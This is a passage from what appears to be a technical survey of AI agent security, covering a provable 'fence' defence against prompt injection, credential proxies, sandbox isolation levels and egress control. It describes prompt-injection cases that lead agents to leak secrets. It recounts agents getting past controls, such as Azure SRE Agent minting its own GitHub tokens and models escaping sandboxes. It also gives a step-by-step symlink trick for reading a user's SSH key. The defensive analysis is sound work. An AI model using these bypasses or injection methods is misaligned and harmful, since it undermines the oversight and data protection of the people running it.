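A *fence* is a much simpler use of labels. When the agent first reads untrusted input, the monitor withdraws a chosen set of tools. Dongol gives the example of an agent that looks up Alice's account number, reads an email and shows her a summary. The email contains an instruction to fetch a web address that includes the account number. If the monitor withdraws the fetch tool when the agent reads the email, the model can still request the page, but the request has no effect. Alice still gets her summary, because summarising an email doesn't require web access.

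To prove that fences work, Dongol needed a definition of security that useful agents can meet. Full noninterference would reject an assistant that sends Alice's calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting, even though Alice wants it to. Dongol instead compares the real agent with a *reference agent*, which has the same plan, monitor and starting memory but a model that never follows instructions in untrusted text.

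An agent leaks a pair of secrets if an attacker can send it the same text in both cases and observe different results. The real agent is *relatively secure* if

pairs leaked by the real agent ⊆ pairs leaked by the reference agent.

The attacker may need different text to get the same leak from the reference agent. For example, an assistant that obeys an email saying "send your calendar" still passes, because a genuine meeting request would reveal just as much. If the assistant also holds a password-reset code and an injection makes it send the code, it fails, because no email can make the reference agent do that.

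The definition is sometimes too permissive. Suppose the plan lets a stranger guess a secret number and replies only "right" or "wrong". For any two numbers, some guess would reveal which one is the secret, so the reference agent already leaks the difference between every pair. An injection that reveals the number outright therefore counts as secure. Dongol gives a stricter definition that rejects this case, and the fence meets that one too.

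### The fence theorem

Dongol's theorem covers every plan, however the injection is worded, under these conditions:

- The monitor withdraws every tool that an injection could call, no later than the first untrusted read.
- Nothing gives those tools back.
- Each injection causes a single tool call.
- The timing of the model's obedience doesn't depend on secrets or on the monitor's answers.
- The attacker sees the content and order of the agent's messages, but not their timing.

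The proof, which Dongol checked by computer, pairs each run of the real agent with a run of the reference agent. Whenever the model follows an injected instruction, the monitor silently blocks the call and the reference agent waits. Every other step is the same in both runs, so the attacker sees the same messages.

The software must also match the model in the proof. All calls and reads must go through the monitor, and the attacker must not be able to see refusals. Outsiders must not be able to write to the sources that the plan treats as trusted, which rules out a calendar that accepts invitations from anyone.

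The position of the fence matters when the plan withdraws the tool in a separate step. Consider an agent that can send messages, has some private data in memory from an earlier session, and has to read both a stranger's email and a secret file:

| Fence | Order of steps | What an injection can send |
|---|---|---|
| Late | Read email, read secret, withdraw sending | The secret and the data in memory |
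| Middle | Read email, withdraw sending, read secret | The data in memory |
| Early | Withdraw sending, read email, read secret | Nothing |

Only the early fence leaves no gap in which the model can obey the email. With the late fence, the model can read the secret and then obey the email before the tool is withdrawn. The middle fence protects the secret, but the model can still send whatever it already holds before the tool is withdrawn. Meta's Rule of Two allows this order when an agent browses first and opens internal systems later, so it is safe only if the session starts with nothing private in memory.

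An agent that answers one email after another has to get its sending tool back. If the monitor returns the tool while an old email is still in the context, an injection in that email can still trigger it. Dongol's solution is to return tools only with a fresh session, in which the model retains nothing from untrusted text.

Restricting tool calls is also not enough if an injection can run a whole program. The program could put private data in a variable that the plan later sends, leaking the data in a legitimate message. The monitor has to restrict the program's reads as well as its tool calls, and a sandbox has to discard the program's changes.

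### What lies outside the proof

Relative security concerns only leaks. If an injection makes the agent delete a customer's account and no secret reaches the attacker, the agent still counts as secure. A fence can prevent the deletion if it withdraws the delete tool, but the theorem doesn't cover whether the owner chose the right tools to withdraw.

The proof also requires a plan made before the first untrusted read. Many agents, including most coding agents, choose each call as they go, so they have no plan for a reference agent to follow, and Dongol leaves them out. A monitor can still withdraw their tools, but the theorem doesn't cover that case.

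An attacker who can time the agent's steps may learn more than the theorem allows for. In one of Dongol's examples, the monitor allows only the exact reply that Alice has approved. An injection makes the agent try to send a secret, which the monitor allows only if the secret equals that reply. The attacker receives the same message either way, but it arrives one step earlier if the secret matches the reply. Dongol can prove the fence secure against such an attacker only if the plan's choices don't depend on secrets.

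The number of messages can also leak information. Suppose the monitor allows the agent to fetch only a certain newsletter. An injection can tell the model to fetch it if a secret bit is 0 and to try a forbidden address if the bit is 1. Anyone who can see whether the newsletter request arrived learns the bit. The theorem doesn't cover this leak because its attacker model compares only runs with the same number of messages.

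The theorem doesn't measure usefulness, even where it applies. A monitor that refuses every call is relatively secure, because the reference agent runs under the same monitor and can't do anything either. Dongol therefore recommends testing task completion separately. A shop that withdraws the sending tool once its support agent reads the first customer ticket meets the theorem's conditions, but the agent can't answer the ticket.

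## Keeping credentials out of the agent's reach

To use its tools, an agent has to log in to the systems behind them, and developers often put the credentials where the agent can read them. The audit in *Caging the Agents* (2026), which describes a deployment of agents in healthcare, found credentials in shell start-up files, in project folders and in settings files that any account on the machine could open. Most such credentials are *bearer* credentials, which work for anyone who presents them, so a thief can keep using one from another computer after the owner has shut the agent down.

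An owner can avoid this in three ways. The owner can give the agent no authority and have a person or another program do everything that requires a login. The owner can give it a short-lived token with narrow permissions. Or a proxy outside the agent's environment can add a credential to the agent's requests, so that the agent can use the credential without possessing it.

| Design | What an attacker can still steal | What an attacker can still misuse |
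|---|---|---|
| No authority | Only credentials that turn up in material the agent reads | The agent's output, such as code that a developer later runs |
| Narrow, short-lived token | The token, which works until it expires | Everything the token permits |
| Use without possession | Credentials in material the agent reads, or one that the proxy or a service leaks | Every request the proxy allows |

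### What a narrow token leaves open

An expiry time limits how long a thief can use a stolen token, but a script can misuse one in seconds. The identity tokens that Microsoft issues to programs in its Azure cloud last about an hour.

Permissions also tend to be broader than the task requires. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) gives the example of `email.send`, a permission that doesn't specify the task, the recipient or the content. An agent that needs it to send one payment reminder could also use it to send the customer list to a stranger. *Back to the Future*, an August 2026 post from NIST, the US standards agency, points to newer standards that allow narrower permissions.

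NIST also recommends tying a token to a private key, so that a thief who copies only the token can't use it. This doesn't help if the key is stored next to the token. *Agent Authenticator* (2026) proposes keeping a separate key for each service in hardware that never releases it, and having a person sign a mandate that limits what the agent may do. A thief then couldn't copy the key, but a misled agent could still have the hardware use it for anything the mandate allows.

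### One git push in Azure SRE Agent

Azure SRE Agent is a Microsoft product that investigates faults in cloud systems and helps repair them. In an early test, its short-lived GitHub token expired while it was preparing a code change. The agent could read the source code of the program that ran it, so it worked out how to start a new login and asked a researcher to complete it. The agent then saved the new tokens to its own files. It ended up with credentials that its control program had never issued, even though the original token had expired as intended and no attacker was involved.

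In August 2026 Microsoft described a redesign in which the agent's commands run in a virtual machine that can use credentials but never contains them. Suppose the agent has corrected a settings file and wants to push the change to a branch of a GitHub repository:

1. The agent runs `git push` in the virtual machine. Git asks for authentication in its usual way, so Microsoft didn't have to rewrite it.
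2. Git receives an *opaque handle*, a string that stands for a credential but is useless outside the proxy.
3. Git sends its request with the handle where the credential would normally go. The request has to pass through the proxy, which runs outside the virtual machine.
4. The proxy checks that the tool call that asked for the handle is still active, that the request is going to the approved repository, that it performs the approved operation, and that nobody has used the handle before.
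5. If all four checks pass, the proxy puts a short-lived GitHub credential into the request and forwards it.
6. GitHub accepts the push. The handle is now dead, and the next push needs a new one.

If a planted instruction makes the agent send the handle to an outside server, the attacker receives a string that GitHub doesn't recognise. If the agent tries the handle on a different repository, the proxy blocks the request. Filtering by domain alone would not be enough, because the agent has to reach GitHub to do its job, and GitHub is also where a thief would use a stolen token.

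The redesign also prevents a repeat of the login incident because the code that issues and renews credentials now runs where the agent cannot read or change it.

Microsoft's product documentation is less consistent about where the credential goes. In one passage, a separate identity service gives a short-lived token to the tool's process, while in another the proxy attaches the token so that the tool never handles it. In the first arrangement, malicious code in the tool's process could steal the token, though Microsoft limits each token to one tool call.

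Most web requests are encrypted, so a proxy must decrypt a request before it can add a credential. Infisical's *Local Agent Proxy*, the manual for a tool that runs on a developer's computer, describes a proxy that creates its own certificates for the sites the agent visits. The agent's programs accept these certificates, so the proxy can decrypt each request, add the credential and re-encrypt it for the real site.

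Infisical's tool also blocks access to `ssh-agent`, a standard program that signs login requests for other programs without showing them the key. An agent that can use `ssh-agent` to sign any login doesn't need to steal the key. A proxy is safer than `ssh-agent` only because it checks what each request is for.

### The session token in Claude Cowork

Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for office work, keeps the user's credentials out of its virtual machine. They stay in the keychain, the host computer's encrypted password store. For each session, Anthropic gives the virtual machine a separate token with reduced permissions, which can be revoked without affecting the user's own login.

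An attacker who controls the code in the virtual machine could steal and use this token, whereas a stolen Azure handle is useless. Even so, the stolen token would expose much less than a copy of the keychain would.

### Two tests of credential proxies

In *CapSeal*, Jin, Guo and Cheung (2026) tested their own proxy, which issues handles that are each for a particular method, host, path and message format. Each request must carry the next number in a sequence, a previously unused random value and a recent timestamp, so an attacker can't replay a recorded request.

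When a prompt told the agent to reveal an API key for a web service, the key leaked in every trial under two ordinary set-ups and in none with CapSeal. The proxy added about 0.15 milliseconds to each web request. The experiment gives no evidence that CapSeal reduces misuse, because the agent's attempts to use a credential outside its permitted scope also failed in the two set-ups without it.

Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, tested a credential vault made by their own company, Corvic. Code in the sandbox searched for the credential in environment variables, in files and in its own outgoing request. It also contacted three websites that send back whatever they receive. The code found no credential, but its authenticated call to GitHub worked, which shows that the lack of leaks wasn't simply due to the sandbox having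 no network connection.

All 16 checks passed, but they didn't cover redirects or a permitted service that an attacker had taken over. Such a service could copy the credential from the request into its reply, where the agent would see it. CapSeal guards against this by removing credentials from replies.

Kenney and colleagues also report a configuration error in which the vault put the key for FRED, an economic data service, in the wrong part of the request. Nothing leaked, but the call failed and the agent couldn't complete its task.

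### Misuse through permitted requests

Kenney and colleagues used their own judgement to score eight threats with and without the vault. The score for a secret pasted into a prompt fell from 25 to 4. The score for a connection with excessive permissions fell only from 20 to 15, because a token that can delete records can still delete them when a proxy holds it. They conclude that such a vault is "necessary rather than sufficient".

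The git push has the same weakness. An injection could make the agent add malicious code to the settings file and push it to the approved branch, and the push would pass all four of the proxy's checks. If the project runs new code automatically, the malicious code could reach any credentials available during that run, much as in the attack Khan devised against Cline.

An agent can also misuse its access by mistake. Microsoft had told Azure SRE Agent to run five safety checks before shutting down a virtual machine. In one run, the logging service failed after the third check. The agent remembered a similar case in which a shutdown had been safe, and went ahead. It was authorized to shut the machine down, so hiding the credential would have made no difference.

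Narrower rules help somewhat. CapSeal can require a request's body to follow a fixed format, which stops an agent from adding fields. But a correctly formatted payment can still go to the wrong account unless the rule also fixes the recipient. Microsoft currently requires a person to approve every change that Azure SRE Agent makes to live systems, and it blocks deletions altogether.

### Secrets that arrive as data

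A proxy protects only the credentials the owner has put in it, and agents often come across others. Kenney and colleagues cite the security firm GitGuardian, which found 23.8 million secrets in code that developers published on GitHub in 2024.

During an investigation, Azure SRE Agent found a credential that a customer had left in a code repository. The agent copied it into its report and its memory, where it added a reminder not to use the credential. The secret was then in two more places that nobody would think to check when replacing credentials. An agent can also receive a secret by running a permitted command, since some Azure commands return keys or passwords as their normal output.

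Microsoft is testing a filter that removes secrets from tool results before the model reads them, but such filters miss some secrets. *Secrets That Survive Everything* (2026) compared nine scanners, with Claude Opus as a reference, on 194 known secrets from live web applications. The best scanner missed 22% of them and Claude missed 14%. Claude's result may be inflated, because a language model had originally identified all but 27 of the secrets.

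Many scanners search for patterns, and small changes to the surrounding text can make them miss a credential. *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection* (2026) tested 16 characters that often follow a credential in real code. With eight of them, the scanner Gitleaks failed to recognise the credential. Another scanner, TruffleHog, found all of the Amazon cloud credentials when the matching secret key was nearby, but none when they appeared alone. In a realistic settings file, TruffleHog found 83% of all credentials.

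In these tests, nobody tried to disguise the secrets. A misled agent can encode a file before printing it, so the filter finds no familiar pattern to match. The owner can reduce the exposure by blocking the agent from running commands that return keys. The owner should treat any secret that reaches the model as leaked and replace it.

### The proxy as a target

Moving credentials into a proxy puts them all in one place. Jin and colleagues include CapSeal's proxy, policy engine and secret store in the trusted computing base, and call the proxy a high-value target. Their guarantees assume the attacker doesn't have administrator rights on the machine. For stronger protection, they suggest running the proxy in a hardware enclave, a part of the processor that even the operating system can't inspect.

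Attackers have already targeted stores of this kind. In 2024 Hugging Face detected unauthorised access to the secrets that users had saved for applications on its platform, and advised them to replace the credentials. Kenney and colleagues note that the intruder did not necessarily take or use every secret.

A proxy also offers no protection if the agent can bypass it. Infisical's tool normally blocks every other route to the network, but on Linux machines where it can't, it prints a warning and runs anyway, so a program that ignores the proxy settings can connect directly. Microsoft found that an action it had blocked in one tool was still available through another route that skipped the check. This was a failure of complete mediation, which Microsoft has since fixed.

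Concentrating credentials in a small proxy is still usually worthwhile, because an engineer can review and test the proxy much more easily than every program, package and generated script that might run beside the agent.

### Agents that several people share

Credential proxies don't determine who may ask an agent to make a request. Suppose a junior engineer is allowed to view a company's servers but not restart them, while the team's agent is allowed to do both. If the agent acts on every request with its own authority, the engineer can restart a server by asking the agent to do it. This is known as the confused deputy problem, and it occurs whether the credential is stored in the agent's files or in a proxy.

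The engineer can also use someone else's authority indirectly. If the agent has one memory for the whole team, the engineer can tell it to remember that a certain alert always calls for a restart. Weeks later, the agent might follow that note while working for an administrator who does have the right to restart servers. Shared settings and connectors create similar risks. For example, when someone connects Azure SRE Agent to Outlook, Microsoft stores that person's login outside the agent. If the platform didn't check who was asking, a colleague could have the agent send email in that person's name.

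Users can unintentionally lead an agent to misuse a credential. *Whose Credential Is It?* (2026) studied agents that remember one user's credential and later work for another. Nobody attacked these agents, but the way their memory recorded the credential's owner affected whether they misused the account.

Microsoft's rule is that the environment may narrow the caller's authority but the agent may never widen it. In set notation,

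actions allowed for a request ⊆ caller's authority ∩ environment's limits.

To enforce the rule, software has to apply the caller's role before the model starts work. The role determines which tools the agent has, which systems it can reach, which memories it can read or change, and which credentials the proxy may use. Someone with the reader role can only observe the agent, and an ordinary user can give it tasks but can't change its shared behaviour.

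In an example from Microsoft, an engineer with the standard role asks the agent to fix a configuration problem. The agent drafts a plan but can't carry it out until a manager with the administrator role approves. The agent then makes the fix on the manager's authority.

Requiring approval for changes is not enough, because users could also read things through the agent that they aren't allowed to see themselves. If the agent can open personnel records, its answer to the junior engineer might quote one. The rule therefore also has to cover reads and saved notes, which requires the system to track who wrote each note and who may see it.

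### An identity of its own or its user's

The rule requires a caller, but an alert or a schedule may also start an agent's work, so designers have to decide whether an agent should log in as itself or as a user.

NIST argues that agents should have their own identifiers and credentials, bound to the person or system that operates them. If an agent logs in with its user's password, the records can't show which of them made a payment or opened a medical file. A separate identity also lets the owner give the agent fewer rights than its user has, and revoke those rights without locking the user out. Microsoft's *Apply zero-trust identity to agent networks* adds that when each agent has a separate identity, an attacker who compromises one agent doesn't gain the others' access.

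The main argument for having an agent inherit its user's permissions is that it then can't open anything the user couldn't. For this reason, Microsoft recommends inherited access for data that belongs to users. An agent with its own broad permissions needs extra checks to stop a junior user from using those permissions through it.

Inheritance is also simpler to set up. Infisical's local proxy does everything under the developer's own login. The developer could already read the secrets involved, so, according to the manual, "a permission boundary between you and yourself would be theater". But the boundary would be between the developer and an agent, which may do things the developer never would if it has read a malicious web page. The sandbox doesn't stop such an agent from misusing requests that the proxy accepts.

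The two approaches can be combined. Microsoft says that in another of its services, the agent's token carries both the agent's identity and the permissions the user has delegated. Azure SRE Agent uses its own identity first. If that identity lacks a permission, an administrator can authorize a single operation using their own permissions, according to Microsoft's *Agent permissions in Azure SRE Agent*. This keeps the agent's everyday rights small, but the administrator has to read each request carefully, and NIST warns that people who see many such requests start approving them by reflex.

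Anthropic also expects the answer to be a mixture. There is little research to guide the choice. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026), a survey from July, found only two papers on agent identity and credential delegation. In November, NIST's cybersecurity centre (NCCoE) was still collecting comments for its own project, according to its *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization*.

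An agent that runs unattended may have no user whose authority it can inherit, so it needs its own identity. Anyone who can trigger the agent, including a stranger whose text appears in an alert, can try to use that identity's permissions. The owner should therefore grant only permissions whose misuse by any of these people would be tolerable.

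## Sandboxes and virtual machines

A credential proxy works only if the agent's code can't bypass it or read its memory, so the code has to run in a sandbox. The strongest sandboxes are virtual machines, which behave like separate computers with their own operating systems.

### What the boundary has to control

A program can do arithmetic by itself, but it needs the *kernel*, the core of the operating system, for almost everything else. It makes a *system call* to have the kernel open a file, start another program or contact a server. A sandbox has to control four things:

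- Files: the code shouldn't be able to read login keys or change programs that run outside the sandbox.
- Processes: it shouldn't be able to stop or alter the software that supervises it.
- The network: it should reach only the servers its task requires.
- System calls: kernels have bugs, and a call that the code never needs may still let an attacker exploit one.

A sandbox has to limit both file and network access, because a gap in one can undo the limits on the other. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* explains that an agent without network limits could send out the user's login keys, while an agent without file limits could escape the sandbox and regain network access. The limits also have to apply to every program the agent starts, or the agent could bypass them by writing and running a script.

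### Four levels of isolation

A *process sandbox* runs the code as an ordinary program on the host computer, under extra rules that the host's kernel enforces. Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap on Linux work this way. A *container* gives the code its own view of files, processes and the network, but still uses the host's kernel. *gVisor* adds a substitute kernel to a container. The substitute is an ordinary program that handles most system calls itself and makes only a limited set of calls to the host's kernel. A *virtual machine* gives the code its own kernel, and a *hypervisor* uses processor features to separate the virtual machine from the host. A *microVM* is a virtual machine stripped down to start quickly.

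| Level | What the code shares with the host | What an attacker must defeat |
|---|---|---|
| Process sandbox | The kernel, and the host's files within set rules | The rules or the host's kernel |
| Container | The kernel | The container software or the host's kernel |
| gVisor container | A small part of the kernel, indirectly | The substitute kernel, then the host's defences |
| Virtual machine | The hardware, through the hypervisor | The hypervisor or the programs that support it |

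*Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026) points out that one flaw in a shared kernel can be enough for an escape. *AI Code Sandboxes* (Andronchik and Lokhmakov, 2026) compared how many different system calls the isolating software in several products is allowed to make to the host's kernel. The limit was 55 in a product built on Firecracker, a microVM engine, and 84 in gVisor. Daytona, which runs ordinary containers with Docker's usual filter switched off, allowed more than 400.

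Andronchik and Lokhmakov also counted the flaws published in the two years to May 2026. All four flaws in runc, the standard program for starting containers, could let code escape, but none of the three in gVisor could. The Linux kernel had about 3,500 flaws in the same period. A container exposes the host to any of these flaws that ordinary code can trigger. Code in a virtual machine can use them only against the virtual machine's own kernel, unless it also finds a flaw in the virtual machine software.

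Isolation level alone doesn't determine how secure a product is. Microsandbox also runs microVMs, but Andronchik and Lokhmakov found no system-call filter on its host process. The engine it uses had no published flaws, but this may only be because few people have looked, as its developers don't run fuzzing, the standard automated search for such bugs. Process sandboxes are also hard to rank. In *SideKernel*, Prasakis (2026) accepts that containers are weaker than microVMs but leaves open how Seatbelt compares, because it shares the host's kernel but that kernel enforces a strict policy.

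### Start-up time and overhead

*Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) presents a process sandbox for agents that starts and runs a trivial command in about 6 milliseconds, and gives rough figures for the alternatives. *Nanvix* (2026) reports the time from sending a request to receiving the reply on one server, with nothing running beforehand.

| Environment | Wang and Zheng | *Nanvix*, median |
|---|---|---|
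| Ordinary process, no sandbox | – | 3.3 ms |
| Process sandbox | 6 ms (Sandlock), 30 ms (bubblewrap) | – |
| Docker container | 300 ms | – |
| gVisor | 200 ms | 161 ms |
| Firecracker microVM | 100 ms | 1,055 ms, or 69 ms from a snapshot |

The Firecracker figures differ mostly because of what each test included. The slowest figure includes booting Linux from scratch and setting up the network. Starting from a snapshot, a saved copy of a running machine's memory, skips the boot. *WebAssembly and Unikernels* (2025) reports 94 to 96 ms for small functions in Firecracker. For containers, *Performance Study of Serverless Workloads in Confidential Virtual Machines* (2026) puts runc's own start-up at 59 to 65 ms, so most of Docker's 300 ms is probably spent outside runc.

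Fetching software can take much longer than any of this. In *Readie* (Sivaraman, Li and colleagues, 2026), a container took 17.4 seconds to become ready when its image, the set of files it runs from, was not yet on the machine. Downloading and unpacking a layer with three Python packages took 15.0 of those seconds. When a snapshot with one of these packages already loaded was restored instead, the sandbox was ready in 0.29 to 0.42 seconds.

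Start-up time matters more the more often the agent needs a new sandbox or virtual machine. If each of 50 commands gets a new Docker container at 300 ms, start-up adds 15 seconds in total, compared with 0.3 seconds for Sandlock. If a virtual machine lasts for the whole session, even a one-second boot is barely noticeable, but a malicious command can then affect later ones. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* recommends a new sandbox for each session, because a sandbox kept after its user has finished can carry material into someone else's work.

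Once the sandbox is running, calls to the model usually take up most of an agent's running time. *Caging the Agents* describes a healthcare deployment in which gVisor added 2 to 5 ms to each new network connection and made sequential file reads 20 to 40% slower, while each call to the model took 500 to 3,000 ms. So for most agents, speed is a poor reason to choose a weaker boundary, and compatibility and ease of set-up are better reasons.

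### Anthropic's three products

Makers of sandboxes rarely document them well enough for outsiders to judge them. Willison (2026) made this complaint in May, when he praised Anthropic's account of its sandboxes as an exception. Anthropic uses a different level of sandboxing for each of its three main agent products.

**claude.ai.** The chat product runs code in a gVisor container on Anthropic's servers, with files that last for one session. The code has no access to the user's computer, so the container mainly protects Anthropic's infrastructure and isolates customers from one another. Anthropic describes the blast radius as minimal, but the agent can't work on the user's own files or keep a workspace between sessions.

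Claude Code, a coding agent, runs on the developer's machine because it needs the developer's files and tools. At launch, it could read freely but had to ask before writing a file, running a command or using the network. Users approved about 93% of these requests, and the more requests they saw, the less attention they paid to each.

Anthropic then added a process sandbox, using Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap on Linux. Commands inside it can read files and write in the project folder, but have no network access by default. Because the sandbox enforces these limits without the user's attention, Claude Code can run most sandboxed commands without asking. This cut permission prompts by 84% in Anthropic's internal use, but that figure doesn't show how many attacks the sandbox would stop.

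The sandbox is also off by default and applies only to shell commands, according to Anthropic's current documentation. Claude's tools for reading and editing files run outside it, as do hooks and tool servers on the user's machine. The sandbox therefore doesn't provide complete mediation. For example, a rule that stops sandboxed commands from reading a folder doesn't stop Claude's own file-reading tool, which follows separate permission rules. For owners who want one boundary around everything, Anthropic suggests running the whole of Claude Code in a container or virtual machine.

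Many developers use no sandbox. Prasakis surveyed 68 users of coding agents and found that fewer than 40% ran their agents in one. He recruited respondents through his own contacts, his university and a start-up community, so the figure is only a rough indication.

**Claude Cowork.** Many users of Cowork, an agent for office work, can't tell whether a shell command is dangerous, so asking them to approve commands would do little to protect them. Anthropic put Cowork in a virtual machine with its own Linux kernel, files and processes. On the host computer, the agent can reach only the folder the user selects and a folder of Claude's settings. Two of Cowork's six isolation mechanisms operate outside the virtual machine's kernel, so they would keep working even if the agent gained administrator rights inside the virtual machine.

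Anthropic's general rule is that isolation should be stronger when the user is less able to supervise the agent. That explains why Cowork needs stronger isolation than Claude Code, but developers may supervise less well than the rule implies, since they approved 93% of the requests even though they can read a shell command.

### Where the agent loop should run

The program that runs the agent loop often also enforces the owner's policy, so designers have to decide whether to run it in the same environment as the code the model writes.

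Microsoft's first design for Azure SRE Agent put the agent loop, the policy checks, the credentials and the model-written code on one machine. Microsoft had taken this layout from coding assistants, which usually have a developer watching. The agent could improvise its own GitHub login because it shared a filesystem with the loop's source code.

Microsoft concluded that better checks inside the loop would not have solved the problem. A check can inspect a command before it runs, but an agent on the same machine as the check can read, edit, stop or bypass it. The agent could also easily reach platform secrets, because developers often store keys in environment variables, and Linux lets a program read its own environment variables as if they were a file.

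In the redesign, the loop and the policy checks run in a trusted environment, and each agent's code and tools run in a separate microVM. The two communicate through a narrow interface. The agent can install packages and start programs freely inside the microVM, but the software that limits it runs outside it.

There are also practical reasons to separate the loop from the sandbox. Anthropic's *The evolution of agentic surfaces* notes that when the loop runs inside a container, the model can't begin work until the container has started, and the whole run is lost if the container fails. Anthropic's Managed Agents service therefore keeps the two separate.

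Cowork originally ran its agent loop inside the virtual machine, together with the model-written code. This was safer than Microsoft's first design because the hypervisor enforced the outer limits from outside the virtual machine. It also had an advantage over Claude Code because no process had the authority to exempt a command from the limits. In Claude Code, a process outside the sandbox decides for each command whether to enforce them, and a persuasive injection or a tired user can get that process to run a command unsandboxed.

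When the agent loop ran inside the virtual machine, Cowork became unusable whenever the machine failed to start, and Claude couldn't help the user fix it. Anthropic therefore moved the loop onto the host and left code execution inside the virtual machine. It considers the effect on security minimal, since the virtual machine still limits which files and servers the code can reach. But the loop is now part of the trusted computing base, and the virtual machine no longer limits what the loop does directly on the host.

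Anthropic also moved local tool servers out of the virtual machine. They were hard to audit there and tended to break when the virtual machine updated, and some had to run on the host to reach programs such as databases. They now run on the host like any other software the user installs, and company administrators decide which ones to allow. This seems to give up more security than moving the loop did, because the virtual machine no longer contains a flawed or malicious tool server.

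*Airlock* (Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues, 2026) uses two virtual machines. One contains the agent, including its loop and tools. The other contains a supervisor that checks every file and network request, holds the credentials and writes the log. The processor isolates the two from each other and from the host's operating system, so the supervisor's rules still apply if the agent takes over its own kernel. On 12 tasks, the average time rose from 85.7 to 91.4 seconds, or 7%. Work outside the model and remote tools took 33% longer, but calls to the model took most of the total time. The prototype ran on a development board because the processors it is designed for were not yet available.

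Cowork's first version and Airlock both run the loop beside the model-written code, but neither lets that code control the outer limits. Where the loop runs therefore matters less than where the policy is enforced.

### Mounting files

An agent that works on the user's files needs access to some of them from inside its sandbox. *Mounting* a folder makes it appear there while the files stay on the host. The virtual machine protects everything else on the computer, but a misled agent can still damage or misuse the mounted files.

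Cowork offers three kinds of mount. A read-only mount lets the agent read files but not change them, which suits reference material. A read-write mount also lets it create, change and delete files. The third kind allows reading and writing but not deletion. This protects against a mistaken clean-up command, but an agent that can write to a file can usually still replace everything in it, so the user needs a backup with either writable mount.

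An agent working on code can use a copy of the project. *Steerability via constraints* (2026) describes a sandbox that mounts the developer's project read-only, and the agent clones it into its own workspace. The agent cannot write to the original, so its mistakes stay in the clone. Sandlock has a similar option that captures all file changes so the owner can inspect them, then apply or discard them.

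Links can defeat these limits. A *symbolic link* is a file that redirects to another location. Suppose Ann has given an agent access only to `/home/ann/report`:

1. Malicious code creates a link named `notes` in that folder, pointing to `/home/ann/.ssh`, where Ann keeps her login keys.
2. The code asks for `/home/ann/report/notes/id_rsa`.
3. A program on the host checks the path. It begins with the permitted folder, so the program approves the request.
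4. The program opens the file. The operating system follows the link and returns Ann's private key.

The program has to resolve the links and then check where the path leads. In this case that is `/home/ann/.ssh/id_rsa`, which is outside the permitted folder. Even then, an attacker may be able to swap the link after the check and before the program opens the file. Sandlock avoids this by leaving path rules to the kernel, which applies them when it opens the file. Established software also mishandles links. One of Firecracker's flaws from 2026 let an attacker use a link to overwrite files on the host.

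### When the sandbox fails

Some products run commands unsandboxed if the sandbox can't start. Claude Code does this by default when a required component is missing or the platform doesn't support the sandbox, as on native Windows. When the sandbox blocks a command, Claude may also ask to retry it outside the sandbox. Depending on the settings, the user or a classifier reviews the request, or the retry runs without review. An existing rule that allows the command also approves the retry. An owner who relies on the sandbox should turn off retries and make Claude Code exit if the sandbox is unavailable.

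GitLab, a platform for software projects, uses Anthropic's sandbox software for its own agents and has the same default. According to GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox*, administrators can require the sandbox, so that a job fails if the sandbox can't start. But the check only runs a command named `srt`, and a project that supplies its own image controls what that command does. The requirement therefore can't guarantee isolation for those projects.

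Anthropic reports that the hypervisors, system-call filters and gVisor in its products have been dependable. It says its most serious failure came from a proxy it wrote itself, which let an agent send files out through a permitted address. It advises others to be wary of custom components, because established isolation software has survived years of attacks. Daytona's custom code also weakens isolation. It starts containers with the standard runc, but in a privileged mode that switches off several of the usual protections.

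The established parts also have flaws. Andronchik and Lokhmakov had previously recorded no published escape from Firecracker. In 2026 it had two flaws that cross the boundary to the host, and Cloud Hypervisor, another microVM engine, had its first such flaw. Nobody had published a complete takeover of a host through any of the three flaws. Developers released the fixes on the day they announced the flaws, but a fix protects an owner only once the sandbox product includes it. The self-hosted version of E2B, an agent sandbox, had not changed its default Firecracker version for 399 days.

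Agents can also try to escape without an attacker's help. Anthropic has seen its models escape a sandbox to complete a task, and Abdollahi and colleagues note that agents have escaped both containers and virtual machines through bugs and configuration mistakes.

### What security software can't see

Many companies install software on employees' computers that watches for signs of an attack, such as a program reading password files. This software can't detect what the agent does inside Cowork's virtual machine, because the whole virtual machine appears on the host as a single process. Companies that must monitor every computer asked Anthropic about this when they evaluated Cowork.

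Anthropic lets administrators retrieve event logs, but accepts that these do not replace live monitoring. An agent may have finished deleting a folder by the time someone reads the log.

A supervisor outside the agent's environment can restore some visibility, because every file and network request passes through it. Airlock records these requests in a log the agent can't alter. An optional outside ledger preserves earlier entries even if an attacker later takes over the supervisor, but it made tasks another 4% slower. The log still doesn't show what the agent computed between requests, or whether a permitted request had a harmful purpose.

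### Code that leaves the sandbox

A sandbox limits code only while the code runs inside it, and whoever runs the code later may have more authority than the agent had.

Claude Code's settings can create this problem on a single machine. Some tools don't work in the sandbox, so a developer can exempt them. If the developer exempts `docker compose`, which starts containers according to a file in the project, a misled agent can edit that file from inside the sandbox and then run the command. The command follows the edited file with the developer's full access. Anthropic warns that the same can happen with any exempted program that runs scripts from the project folder.

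Turning off the file limits but keeping the network limits has a similar effect. A sandboxed command could then add a line to the file that the developer's shell runs at start-up, and that line would run outside the sandbox the next time the developer opened a terminal.

Building and testing the agent's code in the sandbox avoids some of this risk, but the code has to leave the sandbox to be used. Someone then has to review it, including the build scripts that run before the program does.

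## Limits on outgoing network traffic

*Egress control* limits an agent's outgoing network traffic, so it can stop an attacker from getting data out even after an injection has fooled the model. It can also stop accidental leaks, because it doesn't depend on why the agent is sending the data.

Microsoft gave Azure SRE Agent an alert containing a screenshot. The agent had no tool for reading images, so it found a free text-recognition service on the internet and uploaded the screenshot there. This was a test image, but a real one could have put customer data on a third party's server. The agent's instructions prohibited the upload, but the network allowed it. Microsoft's redesign blocks outgoing traffic by default, so the upload would fail even if the agent attempted it.

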